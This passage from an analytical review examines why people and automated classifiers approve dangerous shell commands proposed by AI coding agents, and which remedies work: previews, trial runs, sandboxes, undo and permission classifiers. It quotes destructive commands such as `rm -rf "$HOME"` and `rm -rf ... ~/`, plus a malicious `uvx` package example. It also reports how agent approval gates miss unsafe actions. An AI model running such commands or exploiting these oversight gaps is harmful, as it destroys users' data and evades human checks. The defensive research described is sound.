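The game's players missed 11.7% of obviously destructive commands, while Anthropic's testers approved 86.4% of clearly dangerous ones. The testers had more time, so time pressure can't explain why they did worse.

Different expectations probably explain much of the gap. The players knew their job was to find threats, and roughly a third of the commands were threats. The testers were working on something else, and a single dangerous command appeared among dozens of ordinary ones. If most programmers can recognise an obviously dangerous command when they look for it, most of the testers' mistakes came from inattention.

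This comparison is limited because the two groups saw different commands, and people who play a security game may know more about the shell than the testers did. A direct test would give the same commands to two randomly chosen groups and warn only one of them.

People also wrongly approve actions when there is no shell syntax to read. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) asked people outside the software industry to supervise a simulated assistant through a day of emails, travel and purchases. Of its 18 actions, 11 were necessary for the tasks and 7 went beyond them. The prompts described each action in plain language, including the recipient or amount where relevant.

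The 34 participants who decided on every action blocked 59.6% of the actions that went too far and approved 94.1% of the necessary ones. Twelve of them let the assistant permanently delete an old work timesheet, although no task called for it.

Thirty of the 34 people let the assistant call the airport to confirm a flight. They may have found the call helpful, so these approvals weren't necessarily mistakes. Without that action, the miss rate falls to 32%. The study is therefore weak evidence about dangerous commands, but it suggests that people would still approve some bad commands even if they were translated into plain language.

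### What developers report about their own habits

Surveys can reach developers who use agents on real projects, but they depend on people describing their own behaviour accurately. In Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026), in *Let the Agent Do It?*, 107 practitioners answered questions about permission prompts, and could choose more than one description of what they do:

| Reported habit | Share |
|---|---|
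| Read requests carefully | 47.7% |
| Skim them | 33.6% |
| Approve by default | 20.6% |
| Have become less careful over time | 33.6% |
| Check requests to write, delete or gain extra privileges more carefully | 76.6% |

In a separate question, 70.1% said they paid close attention to permissions, compared with the 47.7% who said they read requests carefully. Some people may count a quick check of the important parts as close attention. About a third said they check which file a request names, and a quarter said they focus on the command or the title.

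Checking deletions more carefully is sensible, but it works only if the reader notices that a command deletes something. `rm` is easy to spot, but `-delete` in the middle of a long `find` command is less obvious, and `npm run clean` may delete files without containing either.

Salerno and colleagues also interviewed 18 practitioners. One objected that careful review defeats the purpose of a fast tool because "every 10 seconds I have to click something". Another admitted to approving requests without much thought when rushing to deliver work. Interviewees said that wildcards and unfamiliar commands, among other things, made them more cautious, so shell notation influences some decisions. But the study didn't test whether anyone understood the notation.

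In one interview, a practitioner described approving an action and then seeing the agent do something other than what they expected. The practitioner may have misread the command, lacked a relevant fact or been misled by the agent's explanation. The paper doesn't give the command, so we can't tell which.

Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026), in *From Delegation to Action Approval*, surveyed 203 developers in August and September 2026 about how carefully they reviewed the code agents wrote and the actions agents asked to take. Of the 105 who carefully reviewed most or all of the code, 64 (61%) often approved at least one type of action without close review. Among the other developers, 65 of 97 (67%) did so.

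The six-point difference isn't statistically significant. With groups of this size, careful code reviewers could plausibly be anywhere from 19 points less likely to 7 points more likely to approve actions this way, so the result doesn't show that the groups behave identically. The survey still shows that many people who are careful with code are less careful with commands.

The 61% covers seven types of action, some much riskier than others. The share of developers who often approved an action without close review was lowest for reading passwords and other sensitive files (21%) and highest for access to the internet and other connected tools (36%). The share for destructive or privileged commands was between those two figures, so at least a fifth of developers often approved such commands without looking closely.

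Developers who inspected diffs (line-by-line lists of changes to files) or checked unusual cases in the code were less likely to approve destructive or privileged commands without close review. Wu and colleagues suggest that a diff gives people something concrete to check. These developers may also be more careful in general, though the overall measure of careful code review was not connected to how people approved such commands.

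Knowing about the risks didn't seem to make developers review actions more closely. Among those who had heard of a security or privacy problem involving agents, 70% often approved some type of action without close review, compared with 43% of those who hadn't. The difference remained after the researchers accounted for how often and how long people had used agents. Because the survey questioned everyone only once, it can't show whether awareness makes people careless. Developers who approve more freely may, for example, run into more problems.

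Approving something "without close review" isn't always a mistake. A developer who has run the same test command a hundred times has little reason to study it again. The survey measures how common this habit is, which doesn't show how often developers miss a problem.

### Which failures can these studies detect?

Of the three failures that this reference separates, inattention has by far the most evidence, and misparse has almost none:

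| Source | Inattention | Misparse | Missing state |
|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic's testers | main thing it measures | hardly, since the danger was clear | no |
| Claude Code approval rates | only indirectly | no | no |
| scalex.dev's game | yes, mixed with time pressure | possible, but not separable | some commands, though a log could supply the facts |
| Yan's simulated assistant | yes, mixed with personal preference | no, since there was no shell code | little, since prompts described the actions |
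| Salerno and colleagues, Wu and colleagues | yes, but only as people report it | no | no |

*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) covers 290 reports of agents damaging people's files. Problems with user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 of those, the user had let the agent act without asking, and in 31, the approval prompt didn't give the user enough information. These add up to more than 105, so a few reports must have involved both problems.

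The fatigue that makes users inattentive to commands can also lead them to let an agent run without prompts, so they never see the commands. According to *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files*, people accept the risk because the alternative is answering hundreds of prompts in a session.

The 31 cases of uninformative prompts include two different problems, and the total doesn't show how often each occurred. Some prompts contained complex one-liners that were hard to interpret, which can lead to a misparse. An explanation of the syntax would help with these. Others contained short commands such as `python3 setup.py`, which is easy to read but runs whatever code is in `setup.py`, so the programmer would need to see the contents of the file.

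We can't calculate a miss rate from these reports, or from the accidents described earlier, because nobody knows how many commands the same users refused or approved safely.

Willison describes a command that even an attentive expert could approve, because it doesn't show all the information needed to judge it. A software package's instructions tell the agent to fetch some files with `uvx fetch-model-files .` before running the tests. The program `uvx` downloads a package and runs it, and here the package is malicious. The command is easy to read, and the package's name matches the task. A reader would have to know what the package does to refuse the command for the right reason.

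A study could measure how often approvers misread shell syntax by showing them `cd /srv/app && git pull; rm -rf cache`, telling them that `/srv/app` doesn't exist and that the current directory contains a valuable folder called `cache`, and asking whether they would approve the line. It could then ask them to explain what would happen, to separate those who misunderstood the semicolon from those who refused simply because they saw `rm -rf`. The laboratory experiments on C and Python used a similar approach, but none of the studies of agent approvals did.

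### Ten dangerous commands in 10,000 prompts

How much these rates matter depends on how common dangerous commands are, which nobody has measured well. Suppose that 10 out of every 10,000 prompts contain one. The following table combines that assumption with figures from the studies. For the testers, it borrows the 3% refusal rate from everyday use, because their own false-block rate is unknown:

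| Reviewer | Dangerous commands approved | Dangerous commands refused | Harmless commands refused |
|---|---|---|---|
| Approves everything | 10 | 0 | 0 |
| Average tester | 8.6 | 1.4 | about 300 |
| Tester after 50 or more prompts | 9.5 | 0.5 | about 300 |
| Catches every threat, but refuses a fifth of harmless commands | 0 | 10 | 1,998 |

The last row uses the limits that only about a fifth of the game's players met, and they met them for one minute while expecting threats. Meeting those limits over 10,000 prompts would be much harder. At the game's pace of six seconds per command, reading all the prompts would take almost 17 hours, and dangerous commands would appear 100 minutes apart on average.

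In this example, someone who approves everything makes the right decision 99.9% of the time, compared with about 97% for the average tester, who stops some of the dangerous commands. Overall accuracy is therefore a poor way to judge a reviewer when threats are rare. The rarity of threats also helps explain why people stop reading the commands, because approving without looking almost always turns out fine, while a refusal usually just delays the work. Only about one refusal in 200 stops a dangerous command, both for the average tester and for the reviewer who catches everything.

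The example also shows why the cause of each miss matters. Suppose six of the ten commands are obviously dangerous, two depend on a shell rule that many people get wrong, and two run a script whose contents aren't in the prompt. A reviewer who read every line closely would stop the first six. A reviewer who also knew the shell's rules could stop the next two. The last two would still look harmless until the reviewer opened the script.

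## What would help an approver more than the raw command?

A prompt that shows only the command leaves the user to work out what the shell will do and to find any missing facts elsewhere. Agent software could show more, restrict what the agent can do, or ask less often. These remedies help with different failures:

| Remedy | Inattention | Misparse | Missing state |
|---|---|---|---|
| Splitting a line into steps | no | yes, for chained operators | no |
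| Showing the expanded arguments | no | yes, for quotes, splitting and wildcards | values and file names only |
| Lint warnings | only if they are rare | some | a few |
| Trial run with a report of effects | little | yes | yes, for effects inside the test environment |
| Structured actions | no | yes | partly |
| Sandbox or undo | limits the damage | limits the damage | limits the damage |
| Automatic classifier | yes | partly | partly |

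Most of the evidence comes from tests in which a language model was the approver and from one experiment in which people reviewed office tasks, so any benefit to people reading shell commands is partly inferred.

### Clearer text

Splitting a chain into steps could prevent misparses, as long as the steps include the conditions. Claude Code already splits commands at `&&`, `||`, `;`, `|` and similar operators, according to Anthropic, but it does this to apply its permission rules. Showing the user the same pieces wouldn't be enough. For `test -d build || mkdir build && rm -rf build/*`, a list of the three commands would leave out the grouping, which is the part C programmers get wrong. A more useful version would be:

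1. Check whether `build` exists.
2. If it doesn't, create it.
3. If `build` already existed or step 2 created it, delete everything in it except hidden files.

Software can work out this grouping from the shell's grammar. If the agent writes the explanation instead, it may repeat the mistake that led to the command. An agent that wrongly treats `HOME` as the path to a temporary directory would describe `rm -rf "$HOME"` as deleting temporary files. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a related precaution. A classifier can approve commands in the user's place, but it doesn't see the agent's messages because the agent might talk it into a bad decision.

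A prompt could also include ShellCheck's warnings. One of them covers Steam's `rm -rf "$STEAMROOT/"*`, but ShellCheck misses most documented bugs and flags many lines that work. Frequent false alarms would make the prompt longer and give people another reason to stop reading it. It would probably be better to show only the few warnings about deletion, overwriting and chained operators.

Claude Code uses checks of this kind to decide when to ask. In its Manual mode, changing to another directory and then running Git causes a prompt, even if both commands only read files. This is because Git can run scripts called hooks that it finds in the new directory. Few users would guess that from the command, so giving the reason in the prompt would help.

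### Previews of the expanded command

The shell can provide some of the missing facts before the command runs. If a prompt for Steam's command had listed `/bin`, `/etc` and `/home` instead of `"$STEAMROOT/"*`, the user wouldn't have needed to know that the variable was empty. Previewing the arguments that the program would receive also prevents the approver from misreading word splitting and wildcards.

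The traditional way to get a preview is to put `echo` in front of the command, as Greenberg does. This works well for one simple command, but it can do damage when the line contains operators or runs another program:

| Attempted preview | What happens |
|---|---|
| `echo cd build && rm -f *` | prints `cd build`, then deletes files in the current directory |
| `echo sort f > f` | empties `f`, then writes the words `sort f` into it |
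| `echo "$(make clean)"` | runs `make clean`, then prints its output |

`printf` gives a clearer preview than `echo` because it can put each argument on its own line. If `x` holds `file1 file2`, then `printf '<%s>\n' rm $x` prints `<rm>`, `<file1>` and `<file2>` on separate lines, which shows that the shell split `x` into two arguments. It has the same problems with operators as `echo`.

Agent software could build the preview without these accidents, but some values don't exist until the command runs. Expanding `$(...)` means running a program, and in `cd build && rm -f *` the list of files depends on which directory `cd` enters. The preview should mark such parts as unknown. It also has to use the same directory, variables and shells as the real command, and avoid displaying any passwords in those variables.

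A correct preview can be out of date by the time the command runs. Suppose a prompt for `rm -f *.log` lists two old files, and another program creates `today.log` while the user is reading. If the shell expands the pattern again after approval, `rm` deletes all three. The software can avoid this by passing `rm` the two names the user approved. Similarly, *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) recommends that any approval prompt check an action again if its arguments change after the review. Even if the names stay the same, another program could replace the contents of a listed file before `rm` deletes it.

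Some programs have a preview option. `git clean -n` lists the untracked files that Git would delete, and `make -n clean` prints the commands that `make` would run. Both are quick, but `make -n` doesn't show what those commands would do to the files, and it can still run some of them. The software usually has to run a command to find out what it does.

### Running the command before approving it

*Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes CAPER, a system that tries each command first and judges the result. In the paper's example, a user asks an agent to remove old build files and recompile a project, and the agent proposes `make clean && make`. The program `make` reads its instructions from a file called `Makefile`. In one project, the instructions for `clean` delete only `build/`, which `make` can recreate. In another, they delete `src/`, which holds the source code, and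 `.git/`, which holds the project's history.

An approver who knows the shell perfectly can't tell the two cases apart from the command. CAPER handles them as follows:

1. It takes a snapshot of the container, an isolated environment that holds the project and has no network access.
2. It runs the command in the container, records what the programs do, and holds back their output.
3. It compares the files before and after, and writes a short effects report. This lists the files that changed, with the changed text if they are small, along with attempts to use the network and any reading of files that hold passwords or keys.
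4. A language model separate from the agent reads the user's request, the conversation, the command and the report, and decides whether to allow the command.
5. If the model allows it, CAPER keeps the changes and gives the output to the agent. If not, CAPER restores the snapshot and tells the agent why.

For `make clean && make`, the report would show that the command deletes `src/` and `.git/` in one project and `build/` in the other. CAPER doesn't run an approved command a second time, so its report can't go out of date the way a preview can.

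The median report in one set of tests was 0.9 KB, roughly 150 words, compared with 62.5 KB for the full record of what the programs did. A person could read a report of that length, but not before every command in a long session.

**Test results.** Wu, Chen and colleagues compared CAPER with six existing systems on two benchmarks. SABER has 682 programming tasks in which a straightforward way of doing the job causes harm. YoloFS-Ext has 102 dangerous tasks, each with a harmless twin that uses the same request and command. The table includes the best existing system on each benchmark:

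| System | Harmful outcomes on SABER | Harmful outcomes on YoloFS-Ext | Harmless twins blocked |
|---|---|---|---|
| No approval | 19.7% | 71.6% | not applicable |
| Claude Code's auto mode | 14.8% | 62.7% | 3.9% |
| YoloFS | 21.2% | 35.3% | not applicable |
| CAPER | 6.7% | 7.8% | 1.0% |

The researchers built YoloFS-Ext themselves and revised SABER's grading rules after finding false alarms. Under the original rules, CAPER's harm rate was 9.0% and the next lowest was 16.0%, so the revision doesn't explain CAPER's lead. In the test of auto mode, they replaced Anthropic's classifier model with the OpenAI model that CAPER used. This makes the comparison fairer, but the figures don't measure auto mode as Anthropic ships it.

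CAPER blocked at least one command in 79% of the SABER tasks. Agents safely completed fewer of those tasks with CAPER (48.6%) than when nothing needed approval (57.4%).

A further test on YoloFS-Ext changed what the approver model could read:

| Approver | Information besides the request, conversation and command | Harmful outcomes | Harmless twins blocked |
|---|---|---|---|
| CAPER's model | none | 17.6% | 61.8% |
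| CAPER's model | predicted effects | 3.9% | 61.8% |
| CAPER's model | observed effects | 7.8% | 1.0% |
| Weaker model | none | 25.5% | 53.9% |
| Weaker model | observed effects | 33.3% | 4.9% |

Predicted and observed effects both reduced harm, with a difference of only four tasks between them. But only observed effects allowed the approver to stop blocking harmless commands. A plain-language explanation in a prompt is a prediction of what the command will probably do, so it may make a reader more cautious without helping them tell a safe command from a dangerous one.

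These tests used only models as approvers, so they aren't evidence that an effects report would help people. With the report, the weaker model blocked far fewer harmless commands, but harmful outcomes rose from 26 tasks to 34. The rise may be due to chance, but the report clearly didn't make up for the model's poor judgement. A hurried person might also be reassured by a list of changed files and approve the command.

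When the researchers left the changed text out of the report and listed only the files and their sizes, harmful overwrites rose from 3 to 10, while harmful deletions stayed about the same. A reader can recognise an unwanted deletion from the file's name, but needs to see the new contents to recognise a bad edit.

The snapshot and recording added about half a second to an allowed command and one and a half seconds to a blocked one. The approver's decision took longer, a median of 3.2 seconds.

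CAPER can restore files but can't undo a message sent to another computer, so it has to block the network during the trial or supply simulated replies. It therefore can't realistically test a command that updates a live database on a server. The report also covers only one run, and a program that depends on the time or random numbers may behave differently the next time.

### Do people decide better with more information?

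Hossain and colleagues tested this with 80 volunteers, who each approved or refused 12 actions proposed by an AI assistant. The tasks involved email, documents and purchasing, not shell commands. Half of the actions broke the user's instructions. In one, the user had allowed the assistant to send an auditor only summary totals, but the assistant asked to send `report.csv`, which contained the individual invoices.

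That prompt has the same weakness as `make clean`, because the text is clear but the fact that matters is elsewhere. The researchers assigned 20 people to each of four prompts and recorded these results:

| What the prompt showed | Unsafe actions approved | Harmless actions approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 seconds |
| The exact arguments | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 seconds |
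| The arguments, the user's instructions and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 seconds |
| The same facts, with the consequence stated | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 seconds |

The paper doesn't state that the assignment was random, so the groups may have differed from the start.

A shell prompt that shows the command is most like the second row. People who saw the consequence approved 29 unsafe actions out of 120, compared with 52 in that row, and took about ten seconds longer over each decision. For someone who answers 100 prompts a day, that would add about 16 minutes.

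Most of the improvement came from giving people the facts. Hossain and colleagues estimate the benefit of stating the consequence, rather than listing the same facts in a log, at 7.9 percentage points, but their data are compatible with anything from a 19.7-point improvement to a 3.8-point loss. When violations depended on several earlier steps, people made the same number of mistakes with either prompt.

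People also knew that their job was to review actions, and on average half the prompts they saw contained a violation. The study therefore provides little evidence about inattention when dangerous commands are rare, and even the best prompt can't help someone who approves it without reading it.

A statement of effects may at least be quicker to read than the command. In an example from *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files*, a user asked Codex to replace "hello" with "replaced" in one file. Codex proposed a script that checked whether the file existed, edited it with `sed`, and then searched it for both words. The effect fits on one line: the file's first line changes from "hello" to "replaced".

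### Structured actions instead of shell text

An agent can also act without the shell. Suppose that it has a deletion tool that accepts only a list of paths. In place of `rm -r "$dir"/old*`, the prompt could show this:

```
Delete:
  /srv/app/old-cache
  /srv/app/old logs
```

No shell processes the list of names, so spaces, asterisks and dollar signs in them are ordinary characters. The user has no quotes or expansions to misread and doesn't need to know the value of `dir`. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* describes a case in which an agent tried to delete a file named `~` but deleted the user's home directory because it hadn't escaped the tilde. A tool that takes names literally would have deleted the file instead.

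The user still has to know what the two directories contain, and would struggle to check a list of 400 paths. The tool also helps only if the agent uses it. Most coding agents already have tools for reading and editing files, and Cursor has one for deleting them. But in 77 of the 290 reports in the same study, the rules for these tools didn't cover shell commands that could do the same things.

Removing the shell would close this gap, but agents often need its flexibility. In *Is Bash All You Need?*, Mak, Suresh and colleagues (2026) gave two models the same workplace tasks with different sets of tools. With Bash alone, the models scored 21.8 to 24.5 points higher than with a fixed set of tools on a benchmark that simulates a software company, and 4.8 to 7.4 points higher on one covering banking, consulting and law.

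That flexibility also produces lines that are hard to review. Between 94% and 97% of Bash calls used pipes, chained operators, command expansion, several lines or similar features. Replacing these calls with single actions would make each prompt easier to read, but could mean more prompts.

The advantage of Bash depends on the task and the alternative. *What Does a Harness Buy?* (2026) reports that removing the shell from Claude Code changed the number of tasks Claude Opus 5 passed by at most one out of 45. A test of that size could miss a moderate difference, but the result suggests that a strong model can do some kinds of work without a shell.

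Agents could also have both Bash and the fixed tools. In the study by Mak and colleagues, models with both scored about as well as models with Bash alone. An agent could therefore use a structured tool for deletions and the shell for other work, although its software would still have to catch deletions in shell commands.

A compromise is to let the agent start any program but require it to pass the arguments as a list, without a shell. The list `["rm", "--", "old api.log"]` can refer to only one file. However, the agent loses pipes, wildcards and chained commands.

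None of these designs gives the approver enough information to predict what an action will do when it runs other code. A call to a tool named `run_target` with the argument `clean` would contain no shell syntax, but it would run the same commands as `make clean`. Those commands could delete `build/` or `src/`, and the approver would have to read the `Makefile` or see the effects to know which.

### Sandboxes and undo

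A sandbox limits the damage from all three failures, because it works whether or not anyone reads the command. According to *The 2025 AI Agent Index* (2026), Claude Code has an optional sandbox that restricts network access and lets commands write only to the folder where the user started the agent and any subfolders. This would have stopped `rm -rf tests/ patches/ plan/ ~/` from deleting most of the user's home directory. It wouldn't have protected the project itself, because the agent needs permission to change it.

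Sandboxes also block legitimate work, such as installing a package or running a test that needs a file outside the sandbox. Anthropic calls its sandbox safe but "high-maintenance", because users have to configure each new capability. When the sandbox blocks a command, some agents ask to rerun it outside. The user then has to decide whether to approve the command, with the added pressure that work has stopped. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* found that these repeated requests push users to turn the sandbox off.

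Undo can reverse damage after a command has run. Many programmers rely on Git for this, but Git doesn't save files outside the project or files the user has told it to ignore, and an agent can delete the `.git` directory that holds the history. Of the reports of damage with a known outcome, 40% involved a permanent loss.

YoloFS, the system the same study proposes, covers all the files an agent can reach. It stores the agent's changes separately from the originals, takes a snapshot after each command, and shows the agent what changed. At the end, the user reviews the combined changes and accepts or discards them. Reading a private file or sending data can't be undone, so YoloFS asks before the agent opens sensitive paths.

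On 11 tasks with harmful side effects, the agent noticed and reversed the damage in eight. In the other three, the original files were still safe and the user could have rejected the changes. On 112 routine tasks, Claude Code needed 0.4 user responses per task with YoloFS and 0.9 without it, with nearly the same success rate.

A program answered the prompts in those tests, so they don't show whether people would review the final changes carefully. One review is less tiring than dozens, but it may cover hundreds of files. The review also matters more if the agent misses its own mistakes. In the CAPER comparison, 35.3% of dangerous tasks under YoloFS still had damage among the changes awaiting review when the agent finished. A careful user could have prevented some of that harm.

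### Automatic classifiers

A classifier can make the decision in the user's place, so it is the most direct remedy for inattention. In Anthropic's experiment, Claude Code's classifier blocked 89.0% of the dangerous commands, while testers refused 13.6%, and its performance didn't decline in longer sessions. It blocked 800 commands that the testers had approved. The testers refused only six that it had allowed, so using both would have raised the share caught to 89.6%.

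The classifier first runs a quick check that allows most commands, then a slower one that reasons about the rest. Both stages receive the user's messages and the agent's actions, but not the output of earlier commands. Anthropic instructs the classifier to treat a chain joined with `&&` as a single action and to consider its real effect, however it is written.

Clearly dangerous commands are an easy test. On 52 real cases in which an agent had gone beyond what its user wanted, the classifier missed 17%. With so few cases, the true rate could be from about 9% to 30%. The classifier wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary actions. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, it had detected the danger but wrongly treated the action as one the user had agreed to.

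*Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, 2026), an independent stress test that used deliberately ambiguous requests, found that auto mode allowed 81.0% of unsafe actions. Of the unsafe actions that the classifier examined, 70.3% were allowed. Ji and colleagues caution that these rates aren't comparable with Anthropic's 17%, which comes from ordinary work.

Later research suggests a reason for such failures. In *Explicit Authorization Scope Improves LLM-Based Permission Checking in Coding Agents*, Yang, Zhou and colleagues (2026) tested the automatic checkers in Claude Code, Codex and Qwen Code, Alibaba's coding agent. The checkers approved 54% to 93% of the 143 actions that went beyond what the user was supposed to have allowed. But 132 of those actions broke rules that appeared in neither the user's request nor the output of earlier commands. For example, a user might ask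 an agent to delete old files without saying that it should delete only the user's own.

When Yang and colleagues added the missing rule to each request, the checkers' miss rates on the same actions fell from 67–92% to 8–26%, and the checkers blocked fewer permitted actions. The agents then repeated the tasks with the rules included, and none proposed an action outside the rules in 384 runs. The added rules came from the benchmark's answer key, so they were more precise than most users' instructions would be. Even so, the results show that an approver can lack facts about what the user wants as well as facts about the computer.

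A classifier may understand what a command will do but not know whose files the agent may delete. The user usually knows this limit, though they may not know what the command will do, and can state it once in plain language without reading any shell code.

Software can supply some of the facts about the computer. Before a command such as `git reset --hard`, which discards uncommitted work, Claude Code now gives its classifier the repository's current status. Anthropic still advises users to review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves. According to Anthropic, Claude Code also asks for approval before running dangerous `rm` commands, even in the mode that bypasses most prompts, unless the user turns that protection off.
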